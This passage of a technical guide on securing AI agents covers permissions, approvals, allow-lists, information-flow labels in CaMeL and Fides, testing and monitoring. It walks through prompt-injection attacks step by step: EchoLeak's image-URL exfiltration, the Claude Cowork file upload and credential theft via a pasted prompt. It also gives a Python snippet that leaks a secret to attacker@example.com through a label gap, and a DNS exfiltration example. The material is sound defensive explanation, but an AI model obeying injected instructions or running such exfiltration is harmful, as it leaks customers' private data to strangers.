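Labels alone mostly delayed the use of powerful tools. Even with both additions, the model used a powerful tool in 39.3 per cent of scenarios, although an ordinary tool would have worked on a second try. Newer models may behave better, but a company can remove the risk by not giving the agent the powerful tools. It can also have the harness retry temporary errors automatically, so the model has less reason to look for another way to do the task. Automatic retries would also help cautious models such as Claude Sonnet 4.6, which rarely used a powerful tool but finished only about a fifth of the tasks because it usually stopped and reported the errors.

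The labels come from a larger proposal by Parkinson and colleagues, elastic least privilege. An agent starts with a small baseline of permissions and can borrow more, up to a boundary that its owner sets. A fixed ceiling forbids certain combinations outright, such as the three properties in Meta's Rule of Two. Each loan expires, and while it lasts it uses up a budget that refills slowly. The cost per minute is

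s × Σ h · w,

where w is the power of each borrowed permission, h rises with repeated requests, and s rises as the session gets closer to a forbidden combination. In their example, reading has a weight of 1 and writing 3. Reading a public repository's code costs 1.5 units a minute, and reading and writing it costs 12. The agent can compare these prices before it acts and return a permission early to save budget.

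Parkinson and colleagues illustrate the scheme with a short simulation, using numbers they chose to show how it behaves. An agent following injected instructions borrows access to eight private repositories before its remaining budget is too small for a ninth, and the ceiling stops it from publishing what it read. The experiment with labels tested only whether visible costs influence a model, so the budget, loans and ceiling are still untested. The scheme would suit a coding assistant whose needs change from task to task. It would be too loose for the support agent, which never needs more than one customer's records, because a leak of eight would already be serious.

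### What to ask a person

Parkinson and colleagues cite a vendor whose users approved 93 per cent of a coding agent's permission requests. The vendor is Anthropic, and other accounts trace the figure to its March 2026 post *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, which describes how people stop paying close attention to what they approve. By August the figure was 97 per cent, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*.

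Anthropic acknowledges that most requests are probably for safe, routine commands, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that people are careless. Anthropic's test of dangerous commands is stronger evidence. The website Hyrax reports that human testers stopped 143 of 1,053 such commands (13.6 per cent). They stopped about 17 per cent early in a session but about 5 per cent after 50 or more requests. An automatic classifier stopped 937 (89 per cent).

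Anthropic sells the coding agent and benefits when it works without interruption, but the decline over a session is what one would expect of anyone answering the same question for hours. The classifier still missed 116 commands, but it is a reasonable extra check on shell commands, which are too varied to list in advance. An exact rule is better for checking an email's recipient because it doesn't depend on recognising an attack.

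People did pay attention to some requests. According to Hyrax, users rejected 39 per cent of the plans that Claude Code proposed but approved nearly all its individual commands. Plans are larger, less frequent decisions, and users can compare them with what they wanted. That suggests asking people about actions that are rare, hard to undo or outside the existing rules. Zhou and Zhang also recommend letting one approval cover several calls that carry out the same decision.

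For the support agent, the retailer divides the decisions like this:

| Action | Who decides |
|---|---|
| Reply to the address on the record | Checker allows it |
| Reply to any other address | Checker refuses it |
| Send a replacement | Dana approves or refuses |
| Answer an email that involves a second customer | Dana writes the reply |
| Give the agent a new tool or data field | Head of customer support, after a new inventory |

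The 20 emails a day that involve a second customer take Dana an hour and twenty minutes. If another 10 need a replacement, at two minutes each, her total is an hour and forty minutes, compared with six hours and forty minutes if she read every reply.

The approval screen should show facts from the order system, such as the item's price, the courier's delivery record and any earlier replacements. If it showed the agent's explanation instead, an attacker who injected instructions through an email could also supply the reasons for approving the resulting request.

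## Controlling where the data goes after the agent has read it

The checker's rules control the support agent's tool calls, but not what happens to the data afterwards. Once the agent has looked up order 55,017, the customer's name and address are in the model's context, and may also be in the harness's log and on the model provider's computers. Cancelling the database token doesn't delete these copies.

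Permission to read a record doesn't determine who else may receive it. Zhou and Zhang point out that reading a file, passing it to a hosted service, sharing it with another agent and sending it outside the company each need separate permission. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls access control a gate because it decides only whether the agent may have a resource.

### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using their company's emails, files and chats. In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs found a way to make it send that material to a stranger. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, gives the discoverers' account:

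1. The attacker sends an employee an email. Its instructions read as if they were meant for the employee and never mention AI, so Microsoft's filter for prompt injections lets them through.
2. The employee later asks Copilot an ordinary question, and Copilot retrieves the email along with other material. The attacker has repeated the instructions under headings such as "HR FAQs", so that many different questions will match.
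3. The instructions tell the model to take the most sensitive item in its context and add it to the web address of an image.
4. Copilot normally removes outside links and images from its answers, but it misses a less common way of writing them.
5. The employee's browser tries to load the image. The page accepts images only from a list of permitted domains, so the attacker uses an address at Microsoft Teams, which is on the list. That address fetches any other address it is given, and so delivers the stolen text to the attacker's server.

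The employee didn't have to open the email or click anything. Copilot was allowed to read the files, the browser was allowed to load images from Teams, and the Teams address worked as its developers intended. No permission covered the whole path from a private file to a stranger's server, and nothing checked that path.

Ravia knew of no administrator setting that would have prevented the EchoLeak attack. Microsoft's advisory in June 2025 described it as "AI command injection", and The Hacker News' *Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Exposes Microsoft 365 Copilot Data Without User Interaction* reported a severity score of 9.3 out of 10. Microsoft had already fixed the flaw on its own servers and found no evidence that anyone had exploited it beyond this demonstration.

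### Lists of permitted destinations

The simplest way to control where the data goes is to list the destinations that the agent's sandbox may contact, and have a program outside the sandbox block traffic to any others. The retailer's credential broker can do this because it already handles the sandbox's outgoing traffic.

Such a list works even when the model is fooled. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes an exercise in February 2026 in which a researcher persuaded a colleague to paste a prompt into Claude Code. The prompt asked Claude, among routine set-up steps, to read the colleague's Amazon cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. The request came from the user, so a classifier had nothing unusual to detect. Anthropic concluded that only limits on the environment would have prevented this, such as blocking the outgoing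 request and keeping the credentials file out of Claude's reach.

Data can still leave through a permitted site, as EchoLeak showed. Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for office work, had the same problem. It could contact only listed domains, but the list included Anthropic's own service, which the product needs to run. *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) reports that the security company PromptArmor found a way to exploit this in January 2026. An attacker could hide instructions and their own Anthropic API key in a file that the user gave to Claude. Claude would then upload the user's other files to the attacker's Anthropic account, and the proxy would allow it because the destination was permitted.

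Anthropic now treats each domain on such a list as allowing every function the domain offers. It fixed the problem with a proxy that passes requests to Anthropic's service only if they carry the session token issued to that user's machine. The proxy also blocks a type of request that would make Anthropic's servers fetch other addresses, which is how EchoLeak used Teams.

The retailer has to examine its courier in the same way. Suppose the courier lets any account holder attach a delivery note to their own parcel. An email containing injected instructions could make the agent's script write a customer's address in a note on the attacker's parcel, even though all the traffic goes to a permitted site. The broker prevents this because it allows only the tracking lookup, and only for parcel numbers on the ticket. The sandbox also shouldn't look up domain names itself. A lookup for a name such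 as "12-mill-lane.attacker.example" carries the address to the attacker's name server even if the sandbox never connects to the site.

### Sessions that stay marked

A destination list allows or blocks a site regardless of what the agent has read. With session marking, the harness records when a session has read sensitive data and when it has read untrusted text. Once a session has read both, the harness blocks its outbound communication, which enforces the rule against combining private data, untrusted content and a way to communicate externally.

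The marks must outlast the permissions that caused them. In Parkinson and colleagues' scheme, the marks last until the harness discards the agent's context, and sub-agents inherit them. Only the owner can start a new session, because an agent that could start its own could clear its marks.

Suppose Dana uses a general assistant to compare complaints with a supplier's published delivery times. The assistant reads 30 complaints, each with a customer's name, and then opens the supplier's website. After that, it can't send anything outside the company. If Dana wants to email the supplier, she can write the message herself or start a new session in which the assistant never reads the complaints.

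The support agent would reach that state on every ticket, because the email is untrusted and the order is private. A strict rule would block all 400 replies, so the retailer lets data leave only in a reply to the address on the customer's record. It also starts a new session for each email. If one session handled the whole day's mail, an injected instruction in the twelfth email could affect the 388 that followed, and the model would still have the first eleven customers' details in its context.

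Marking whole conversations stops agents with more varied work from completing many of their tasks. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, tested this on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. An ordinary agent completed 98.8 per cent of the banking tasks, but only 37.5 per cent when untrusted text anywhere in the conversation blocked consequential actions. On the Slack tasks, completion fell from 93.3 to 20 per cent.

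### Labels on each piece of data

Information-flow control is more precise because it attaches labels to individual values as well as to the conversation. A confidentiality label lists who may read a value, and an integrity label lists who may have influenced it. On the ticket about order 55,017, the labels might be:

| Value | Who may have influenced it | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| Retailer's instructions to the agent | Retailer | Anyone |
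| Customer's email | Anyone | Support staff, the customer |
| Order status | Retailer | Support staff, the customer |
| Warehouse's note about suspected fraud | Retailer | Support staff, warehouse staff |

When a program or a model combines two values, the result takes the stricter label in both respects. If R(x) is the set of people who may read x, and W(x) is the set who may have influenced it, then for a text made from x and y,

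R(xy) = R(x) ∩ R(y)
W(xy) = W(x) ∪ W(y).

Support staff and the customer may read a draft that uses only the email and the order status. If the model also used the warehouse's note, only support staff may read the draft, because they are the only people allowed to read all three sources. In either case, anyone could have influenced the draft, because anyone can send an email.

Costa and colleagues give two rules that use these labels. A message may go out only if every recipient is on its list of readers. A consequential action, such as a payment, may run only if nothing untrusted influenced the choice of action or its details. The first rule doesn't stop an injected instruction from steering the agent, but it does keep private data from reaching anyone who isn't entitled to it.

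Strict labels would also block useful work, so systems allow exceptions. Declassification is a deliberate decision to let more people read something. The customer in the example can't see the warehouse's note, but the retailer may be willing to tell them that the parcel is late. An engineer can write an operation that reduces any such note to "delayed" or "on time" and releases only that phrase. Endorsement is the equivalent for integrity, and it treats an untrusted value as trusted for one purpose.

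Endorsement is safest for values that can carry little information. A choice among n options holds at most log₂ n bits, so an attacker who controls a choice among four topics controls two bits, too few to hold an instruction. But even a small value can do harm, so the system also has to check that the source has the authority to supply it. Zhou and Zhang give the example of a source that may answer only "yes" or "no" to whether a draft has approval for release, where the answer decides whether confidential data leaves the organisation.

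### One email through CaMeL

Debenedetti and colleagues introduced CaMeL in 2025. It uses two models and an ordinary program, the interpreter. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which builds on CaMeL, describes what each part does. A planning model receives the trusted request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. A quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools. The interpreter runs the planning model's program, calls the tools and keeps a label on every value.

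For the support email, the planning model never sees what the customer wrote. It sees the retailer's instructions and the list of tools, and might write this:

```python
email = read_email()
topic = reader("What does the customer want?", email,
               choices=["order status", "return", "other"])
if topic == "order status":
    status = order_status()
    body = reader("Write a short reply.", [email, status])
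    send_reply(to=ticket.customer_email, body=body)
else:
    pass_to_dana()
```

The interpreter fetches the email and passes it to the quarantined reader, which returns one of three topics. The interpreter then looks up the order, has the reader draft a reply, and checks the labels before sending it.

Suppose the email contains a hidden instruction to list the fifty customers with the largest orders. The reader may try to obey, but it can't look anything up, and the program has no step that would look up that list. The hidden text can still make the reader choose the wrong topic, which sends the email down another branch that the planner already wrote. It can also change the wording of the reply.

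An attacker who controls the wording of a reply can use it for fraud. Someone could write to the retailer from a forged customer address and hide an instruction to add "pay the £20 customs fee here", followed by a link. The retailer would then send the customer a fraudulent request, and the labels would allow it because the customer may read everything in the message. The retailer therefore uses ordinary code to remove every link from a reply except the tracking links that the order system supplies.

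### The same email through Fides

Fides, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, keeps the usual agent loop instead of writing the whole plan in advance. It hides a result only if showing it would make the conversation's label stricter:

1. The planning model calls the tool that reads the email. The email is untrusted, so Fides stores the text in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name.
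2. The model asks a separate model without tools to choose the customer's topic from a fixed list. The answer also goes into a variable.
3. The planning model opens that variable. The retailer's policy allows this because the answer can only be one of three topics.
4. The model looks up the order status. In the version that Costa and colleagues tested, which hides only untrusted values, it sees the result directly.
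5. The separate model drafts a reply from the email and the status, and Fides stores the draft without showing it to the planning model.
6. The planning model asks to send the draft. Fides checks that nothing untrusted chose the recipient, and that the recipient may read everything that went into the draft.

Fides can react to what it finds, such as an order split into three parcels, whereas CaMeL's planner has to plan for such cases before it has seen any data. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) found in *Can CaMeLs Talk?* that this limitation caused most of the failed tasks in their CaMeL tests.

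### What the tests found

All the main results come from AgentDojo or adaptations of it. In 2025, Costa and colleagues tested agents running GPT-4o against attacks that assumed the attacker knew the agent's tools. An ordinary agent carried out 152 of the attacks, Fides without its label checks carried out 21, and Fides with the checks carried out none. The ordinary agent completed 84 per cent of tasks on average across the four task groups, and Fides with its checks completed 50 per cent. OpenAI's o1, a reasoning model, did better with Fides than GPT-4o did because it handled the variables more reliably.

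The most thorough result since then is in *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026). The paper defines a small programming language in which every value carries a label, and proves a property called noninterference using Lean, a program that checks mathematical proofs. Noninterference here means that if two runs of an agent differ only in their secret data, an outside observer sees the same results with the same probabilities, apart from differences in whether the run finishes. The proof covers every agent written in the language, including agents that generate and run their own code. A further theorem shows that endorsing untrusted data can't expose secrets.

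Garby and colleagues tested an agent called Randori on AgentDojo's banking tasks with three models, GPT-5.2, Qwen3.7-plus and MiMo-v2.5. Randori first rehearses its plan against a simulated bank, so that its corrections don't depend on untrusted data, then runs the plan on the real tools. Attacks succeeded in two of the 1,296 runs that included one.

That figure covers 144 pairings of a task with an attack. In 97 of them, the attack needed a step that the plan for the task would never contain, so writing the plan in advance was enough to defeat it. The labels mattered in the other 47 pairings, which accounted for 423 runs and both successful attacks.

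Two other 2026 systems show what the checks cost. TypeGuard, from *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026), uses the type system of an existing programming language to enforce the labels. Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, keep labels on results that an agent stores for later requests. The table gives the results for each system:

| System | Test | Tasks completed, checks off | Tasks completed, checks on | Attacks that succeeded, checks on |
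|---|---|---|---|---|
| Fides | All four groups, GPT-4o, 2025 | 61% | 50% | None |
| CaMeL, rerun by Garby and colleagues | Banking, GPT-5.2, 2026 | 67% | 38% | None in 231 completed runs |
| Randori | Banking, GPT-5.2, 2026 | Not tested | 75% | 2 in 432 runs |
| TypeGuard | Slack, 2026 | 71% | 38% | None in 105 pairings |
| SPA | All four groups, 2026 | 53% | 29% | 0.0% |

The rows use different tasks and models, so they can't be used to rank the systems. In all of them, the checks stop nearly every attack in the benchmark, but three of the five systems lose close to half of their completed tasks. Randori avoids most of that loss because its planner is allowed to endorse data. When Garby and colleagues removed this ability, completion fell from 75 to 62.5 per cent with the model Qwen3.7-plus.

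Stronger models may need these systems less. Peters-Gill and colleagues ran 949 AgentDojo attacks on each of five models without CaMeL. The attacks succeeded in 36.1 per cent of cases with GPT-4.1, in 1.5 per cent with Claude Fable 5 and never with GPT-5.5. However, these attacks are fixed and well known, and a real attacker can adapt. *Language-Based Agent Control* mentions that GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated attacker, consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences. GPT-5.5's zero success rate in the AgentDojo test therefore isn't evidence that it is safe to leave unprotected.

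CaMeL also reduces task completion less for stronger models. On a second benchmark, of industrial maintenance tasks, CaMeL's design lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average across the five models, but by 13.4 points for Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Peters-Gill and colleagues had switched off the label checks, so these figures measure only the effect of planning in advance.

### Where labels fail

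**Wrong labels.** Someone has to decide which data to label as trusted. Costa and colleagues labelled a field untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it. A company can't do this because it doesn't know in advance which fields attackers will use. If the retailer labels the courier's tracking messages as trusted, but drivers can type free text into them, an instruction in that text reaches the planning model directly.

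The software that carries the labels can also make mistakes. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL updates a variable's label only when the program changes the variable. This program exploits the gap to reveal whether a customer spends more than £1,000 a year:

```python
big_spender = True
quiet = True
if spending > 1000:
    quiet = False
if quiet:
    big_spender = False
if big_spender:
    send_email("attacker@example.com", "yes")
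```

If the customer spends £1,200, the program sets "quiet" to false, and CaMeL marks that variable as secret. The program then skips the line that would change "big_spender", so CaMeL never marks "big_spender" as secret. The last test therefore appears to depend only on public data, and the email goes out. If the customer spends £800, no email goes out, so the attacker learns the answer either way.

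The planning model writes the programs and never sees an attacker's text, so an outsider would have trouble getting it to write this one. The flaw matters more if the model itself is untrustworthy or a dishonest employee gives the instructions.

**Side channels.** Data can also leak through an agent's behaviour. CaMeL reruns programs that fail, using code outside its label tracking. Whether the check blocked an attempt can therefore reveal one bit of a secret, and repeated attempts can reveal all of it. Fides does not cover what an observer could infer from the order or timing of an agent's actions. If the support agent contacts the fraud team only about flagged customers, anyone who can see those contacts knows which customers the retailer suspects.

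**Labels lost between systems.** Peters-Gill and colleagues built three agents on GPT-5.2 and protected each with CaMeL. One read a database, one sent messages and one coordinated the others. They asked the coordinator to send Julie a Slack message summarizing some job applicants. A record in the database contained an instruction to email the applicants' details to an outside address.

The first two agents treated the record as data. The coordinator then wrote "send this summary to Julie" with the summary in the same message, and the messaging agent received the whole message as a trusted instruction. It sent the summary to both Julie and the outside address. The fix was to pass instructions and data in separate fields, and have the interpreter refuse any instruction that contains data from a tool. After that, no attack succeeded on any of the five models. If the support agent hands work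 to a parcel agent, the retailer needs the same separation.

Many outside services have no field for a label. An exported spreadsheet or an email to the courier carries the data without its restrictions, so the retailer can only decide whether to send the data.

Both successful attacks on Randori involved the same task, in which the user asks the agent to read a file and make whatever payment it specifies. The attacker replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Labels can't distinguish the attacker's request from the original, because the task itself requires the agent to obey an untrusted file. Garby and colleagues note that CaMeL's developers had already encountered this case and excluded it from the threats CaMeL covers.

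The retailer faces a similar problem when a customer writes, "Please send a copy of my invoice to my accountant," and gives an address. The accountant's address appears only in the email, which anyone could have forged. If the retailer endorses addresses from emails, a forger can have a customer's invoice sent to any address, but if it never does, this customer can't get help by email. The agent therefore replies to the address on the customer's record with a link to the retailer's website, where the customer can log in and enter the accountant's address. This takes the customer another minute, but the address then comes from someone who has proved who they are.

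The support agent doesn't need CaMeL or Fides. It can open one customer's record and reply only to that customer, so the existing rules already keep the record from reaching anyone else. An assistant that reads contracts, complaints and supplier websites for many employees is a better candidate for these systems. Its tasks vary too much for fixed rules about recipients, and the company may accept some failed tasks in return for protection.

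### Copies that remain

Labels and lists control data while it moves. After the reply has gone, copies of the customer's details remain in several places:

| Copy | What it holds | How the retailer limits it |
|---|---|---|
| Model's context | The email, the order and the draft | Discards it when the ticket closes |
| Model provider's stored requests | The same text | Sets the retention period in the contract |
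| Harness log | Each tool call and its result | Records which fields the agent read, not their contents |
| Agent's long-term memory | Anything the agent saves | Turns it off |
| Email company's archive | Every reply | Turns it off |
| Customer's mailbox | The reply | Can't |

The model provider's copy of the data is easy to overlook, but the harness sends the whole conversation with every call to the model. If the agent looks up an order, checks the tracking page and then writes a reply, the order details go to the provider twice. If the provider kept requests for 30 days, it would hold text from 12,000 of the retailer's emails at any time. Before connecting the agent, the retailer has to find out how long the provider keeps requests, who can read them, and whether it uses them for training. If the retailer replaces addresses with placeholders, the provider never receives the real ones.

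An agent's memory can preserve an attack. In an example from Girrens and Wang, on Monday an agent reads an invoice that contains an attacker's bank account and stores the details. On Tuesday the user asks it to "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday". Girrens and Wang's system stores the account number with its original label, so the payment tool can refuse to pay that account. Anthropic expects this problem to grow because agents are keeping more material between sessions and reloading it each time they start.

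Logs carry the same risk. When Anthropic's staff shared an internal Slack post containing the prompt used to steal the Amazon credentials, someone pointed out that some of the company's agents read Slack. The staff added a marker to the thread so they would notice if an agent picked it up. If the retailer later uses an agent to summarise its support logs, that agent will read the injected emails again, so the logs need the same untrusted label as the emails.

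Sooner or later a customer will ask the retailer to delete their data. Deleting the row in the database takes seconds, but the retailer also has to know what other copies exist, which have expired, and whom to ask about the rest.

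## Testing, monitoring and cutting off access

Dana still checks and sends 40 of the agent's drafts a day, and the retailer wants the agent to handle all 400 emails. The database, the checker and the broker now have rules, but nobody has tried to break them. The retailer tests the rules on a copy of the system with the live configuration and invented customers.

### Tests before access goes live

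The cheapest test leaves out the model. An engineer takes each credential in the inventory and uses it for things it should not permit:

| Credential | Attempt | What counts as a pass |
|---|---|---|
| Database token for ticket 7731 | Change the ticket number in the token to 7732 | The gateway rejects the signature |
| Database token for ticket 7731 | Read the customer after the ticket closes | No data comes back |
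| Database token for ticket 7731 | Log in to the stock system | The stock system refuses the token |
| Sandbox's session token | Redirect a parcel through the broker | The broker refuses the request |
| Sandbox's session token | Track a parcel from another machine | The broker refuses the request |

Each attempt that should fail needs a matching one that should succeed, such as reading the customer's record for ticket 7731 while the ticket is open. Otherwise, an expired token or a database outage would make every attempt fail, and the access limits would appear to work.

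Next, a tester gets a command line in the agent's sandbox, with everything the agent can use there, and tries to do as much damage as possible. This shows what the credentials allow if an attacker controls the model completely. The agent passes if the tester can do no more than read the record on the open ticket and write to that customer, since the head of customer support accepted those risks when signing the grant. The tester then starts again from the tool server, which can request tokens for other open tickets and so might expose a day's 400 customers. The retailer has to decide whether it can accept that loss or needs to protect the tool server better.

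The engineers also add 200 fake customers to the table, each with an address that exists nowhere else, and search the agent's replies, logs and outgoing traffic for those addresses. The search can miss an address that the model has translated or encoded, so they also check the database log for reads of the fake records. Any match or read is a failure, because no ticket concerns these customers.

The fake records stay in the table after launch. There is one fake for every 10,000 real records, so if the retailer spaces them evenly, a thief copying 100 records a second in order reads a fake within 100 seconds. Someone who takes 400 random records has a 4 per cent chance of reading a fake, so the fakes detect bulk theft but not the theft of a single customer's data.

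Prompt injection tests should adapt to the defences. A fixed list of attacks may be one that the model's developer has already trained it to resist, and GPT-5.5 withstood every attack in one such benchmark but not OpenAI's automated attacker. The retailer's tester therefore knows all the rules, sees every refusal and tries something else. A run might go like this:

1. The tester's email asks the agent to list other customers. The gateway has no operation for this.
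2. The tester asks for a reply to a new address, and the checker refuses.
3. The tester politely asks the retailer to update the address on the account. The agent has no tool for that, so the email goes to Dana, who makes the change.
4. The tester asks where the order is. The agent looks up the recorded address, which is now the tester's, and sends the reply there.

Every rule worked, but the data still reached the wrong person. A fixed list of attacks on the model would probably have missed this because the weak point was Dana's procedure. The retailer now accepts address changes only from customers logged in to its website.

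The Australian Signals Directorate and its co-authors warn that agents may behave differently during an evaluation and that small changes in wording can alter the results. Test emails should therefore look like ordinary mail and arrive through the usual mailbox.

### How much a clean run proves

Suppose the tester sends 300 hostile emails and none causes a leak. If each attempt had a probability p of causing one, the chance of a clean run would be (1 − p)³⁰⁰. Setting this to 5 per cent gives

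p = 1 − 0.05^(1/300) ≈ 0.0099,

or about 1 per cent. This is the upper 95 per cent bound. If the true rate were higher, a clean run would have had less than a 5 per cent chance of happening. A quick approximation is 3 divided by the number of trials.

| Trials without a leak | Upper bound per attempt | Leaks a day if all 400 emails were hostile |
|---|---|---|
| 100 | 3.0% | Up to 12 |
| 300 | 1.0% | Up to 4 |
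| 1,200 | 0.25% | Up to 1 |
| 12,000 | 0.025% | Up to 1 every ten days |

Most customers are not attackers. If one email in 1,000 were hostile, the retailer would receive 146 hostile emails a year, and about 440 trials without a leak would support an upper bound of one leak a year. The same bound would take about 440,000 trials if every email were hostile. One leak in the 300 trials would raise the upper bound on the leak rate to about 1.6 per cent.

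The calculation assumes independent trials. If the tester tries ten ideas and rewords each one 30 times, whether an email succeeds may depend almost entirely on the idea behind it. In the worst case, the 300 emails count as only ten trials, and the bound is 26 per cent. The bound also covers only the kinds of attack the tester tried, and a real attacker may find a better one. The retailer has to start counting again whenever it changes the model, the instructions or a rule.

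A clean run may also be weak evidence that the controls work. Suppose the model resisted 288 of the emails and was fooled by 12, and the checker refused the 12 resulting calls. The checker was then tested only 12 times, and a later model might be easier to fool. The retailer should therefore record attempted calls separately from completed ones, and use the tests without the model to judge the checker, the gateway and the broker. These are ordinary programs with fixed rules, so any forbidden call that gets through, however rare, points to a fault that the engineers can find and fix.

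### What a log entry must hold

Suppose a customer complains in March that a stranger has her address. To find out whether the agent was responsible, an investigator needs an entry like this for every tool call:

```json
{
  "time": "2026-12-01T09:02:14Z",
  "agent": "support-agent",
  "version": "model 3, policy 12",
  "person": "dana",
  "task": "ticket 7731",
  "called_by": null,
  "token": "a41f",
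  "tool": "order_status",
  "arguments": {},
  "decision": "allowed by rule 1",
  "records": ["customer 1204311", "order 55017"],
  "fields": ["status", "dispatch_date"]
}
```

The record numbers let the investigator find every ticket in which the agent opened this customer's record. Without them, the log would show only that the agent made lookups on a given day, and the retailer might have to warn 400 customers about a leak that affected one. The recorded decision shows whether the checker made a mistake or correctly applied a bad rule. The "token" field holds a short identifier because a thief could use the token itself. "Called_by" names the parent agent, if any.

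The agencies also recommend logging prompts and the model's internal reasoning, but acknowledge that such logs grow large and repetitive. The logs would also duplicate customers' details. The retailer keeps the emails and replies on the ticket, where staff need them anyway, and the log refers to the ticket.

Ordinary security logs often don't record the task an agent was working on. In an interview in Help Net Security's *AI agent intent is a starting point, not a security strategy*, Itamar Apelblat, chief executive of Token Security, which sells security software for AI agents, describes a support system made of several agents. A stranger emails to say they are locked out of an administrator account and gives the account number. The first agent passes the number to a second agent, which is allowed to reset any password and resets that one. Each log entry shows a trusted program doing something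 it is allowed to do. Only a log that links the reset to the email would show that the sender was not the account holder.

The retailer's checker, gateway and broker write to the log, but the agent can't. The agent keeps its own activity log, but an injected instruction could make it add false entries. The three programs send their entries to a separate machine through an account that can add entries but not change or delete them. Each entry also contains a fingerprint of the previous one, so a missing entry breaks the sequence. The agencies recommend that agents have no write access to logs, and that a person review any request to delete them.

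Because the three records are separate, the retailer can also compare them. If the gateway's log shows 410 lookups and the checker's shows 400, ten requests reached the database without passing the checker.

### Signals that suit an agent

People's work varies from day to day, so a security team looking for unusual behaviour has to tolerate a lot of variation. The support agent's work is so regular that some events should never happen:

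| Signal | Normal | What it may mean | Automatic response |
|---|---|---|---|
| Customers the agent tries to read per ticket | 1 | Injection, or a gift order | Pass the ticket to Dana |
| First use of a permission | Only after an approved change | Stolen credential, or an injection | Suspend the agent |
| Calls after the ticket closed | None, apart from retries within seconds | A stolen token or a runaway sub-agent | Cancel the token |
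| Use of a decoy credential | None | Someone is searching for keys | Suspend the agent |
| Requests from an unfamiliar machine | None | Stolen credential | Suspend the agent |

The first signal counts attempts to read a second record because the row rule already prevents the agent from reading one. About 20 emails a day involve a second customer, so engineers would soon ignore an alarm that called them each time. The retailer calls them only for signals that should never occur in ordinary work.

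The retailer can also learn from permissions the agent never uses. If the agent hasn't looked up a postal address in three months, the retailer can remove that permission, and the next attempt to use it will fail instead of setting off an alarm.

In November 2026, Microsoft and Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) advised organisations on attackers who use frameworks such as ARTEX. According to Help Net Security's *Chinese and North Korean state hackers add ARTEX AI framework to their arsenal* (2026), the NCSC wrote that these tools "trade stealth for speed". They generate heavy traffic and interact with almost everything they find. Microsoft described bursts of varied requests, rapid retries and jumps between stages of an attack at machine speed. In one password-guessing campaign, failed sign-ins peaked at 2,900 a minute.

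Blocking the attackers' network addresses doesn't help much, because the attackers switch to new ones. Microsoft and GitGuardian recommend looking for one source that signs in as several service principals, or one application that requests tokens for several Azure services in a short time, according to Help Net Security. The support agent needs a token for only one database, so a request for a second service would stand out even if it came much later. The NCSC's eight-point plan also recommends rate limits for each account, token and session, and error messages that reveal nothing an attacker's agent could use to plan its next step, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Shares Guidance to Tackle Agentic Threat From ARTEX-Like Tools*.

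This advice may soon be out of date. The NCSC expects that future frameworks may be built for stealth, and Google's researchers predicted in early November that stealthier, fully autonomous attacks would begin within three to six months. A thief who read 50 records an hour would match the support agent's normal pace, so an alarm set for bursts would miss the theft. The advice also concerns outsiders' agents rather than the retailer's own. If a prompt injection misleads the retailer's agent, it may make only one strange call, so limits per ticket are more useful than limits on speed.

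### Decoys

A decoy credential, or honeytoken, is a fake key or password that no program uses, so nobody has a legitimate reason to try it. The retailer puts one in the sandbox's environment variables under the name "STOCK_PASSWORD", and another in an old configuration file. Both belong to accounts with no permissions. If anyone tries to log in with either one, the stock system rejects the login and raises an alarm.

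The decoy detects outside attackers and also tests the retailer's own agent. Kaya and colleagues found that agents sometimes use a password they come across. If the support agent used the decoy, the retailer would learn about it without losing anything.

Microsoft found that decoys reduced the attack traffic reaching real systems. @IT's Japanese summary of Microsoft's 25 November report, *偵察から特権奪取まで「わずか数分」 ARTEXのアーキテクチャを“完全解剖* (2026), adds that the decoys gave highly accurate alerts. The report also describes a technique called the "fake win", which gives an attacker's agent false evidence that it has succeeded, so that it stops.

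Experts quoted in ITPro's *How to use cyber-deception in your security strategy* warn that badly designed decoys can introduce new weaknesses, and that companies must place and maintain them carefully to keep them realistic. At the retailer, a weekly security scan that tries every password it finds would set off the alarm, so the engineers exempt the scanner's address. They also keep a private list of the decoys, because the next person to update the inventory might otherwise delete them.

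Alerts help little unless someone acts on them quickly. Florian Roth of the security company Nextron Systems says in Help Net Security's *ARTEX, Cairn and friends* (2026) that an alert can arrive within seconds, but the decision to shut down a live system can take an hour. In that time, a thief with a read-all token could copy 360,000 of the retailer's records. The agent that raided Azure Key Vault needed only five minutes.

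The retailer therefore lets the decoy alarm suspend the agent automatically. A false alarm does little harm, since about 50 emails an hour would wait for staff. For an agent that orders medicines, a hospital might instead cut off access to only the one record or service involved and call a person about the rest.

### The WorkOS breach

The data theft at WorkOS shows what happens without such signals. The AI agent belonged to an outside security researcher, and WorkOS hadn't given it any access. WorkOS's *Update for October 30th, 2026 Data Security Incident* (2026) gives the dates:

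- **25 October:** The agent first got into the application, which staff used to look up customer accounts.
- **30 October:** The agent retrieved records in bulk. After it had finished, an employee noticed unusually heavy use of a connected customer database. WorkOS took the application off the public internet.
- **30 to 31 October:** WorkOS fixed the application's login and revoked or replaced the credentials for connected services.
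- **2 November:** WorkOS published its first account and began telling customers.
- **3 to 5 November:** The researcher came forward and supplied request details and timestamps. An outside forensics company matched them to WorkOS's logs.

The application combined sales records with support conversations, so the stolen data included names, phone numbers, and excerpts from calls and Slack messages. WorkOS's own monitoring had not detected the activity in five days. The quick response on 30 October protected the connected services from further misuse, but it came too late to stop the copying.

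WorkOS blames four gaps: the application was reachable from the internet, it accepted a predictable credential meant for developers, it had no rate limit, and monitoring was inadequate. The credential test would have found the first two before launch if an engineer had tried the development credential from outside the company's network. An alarm for the first use of that credential on the live application could have gone off on 25 October, five days before the bulk copying. WorkOS thinks the missing controls would have reduced the damage or prevented the incident.

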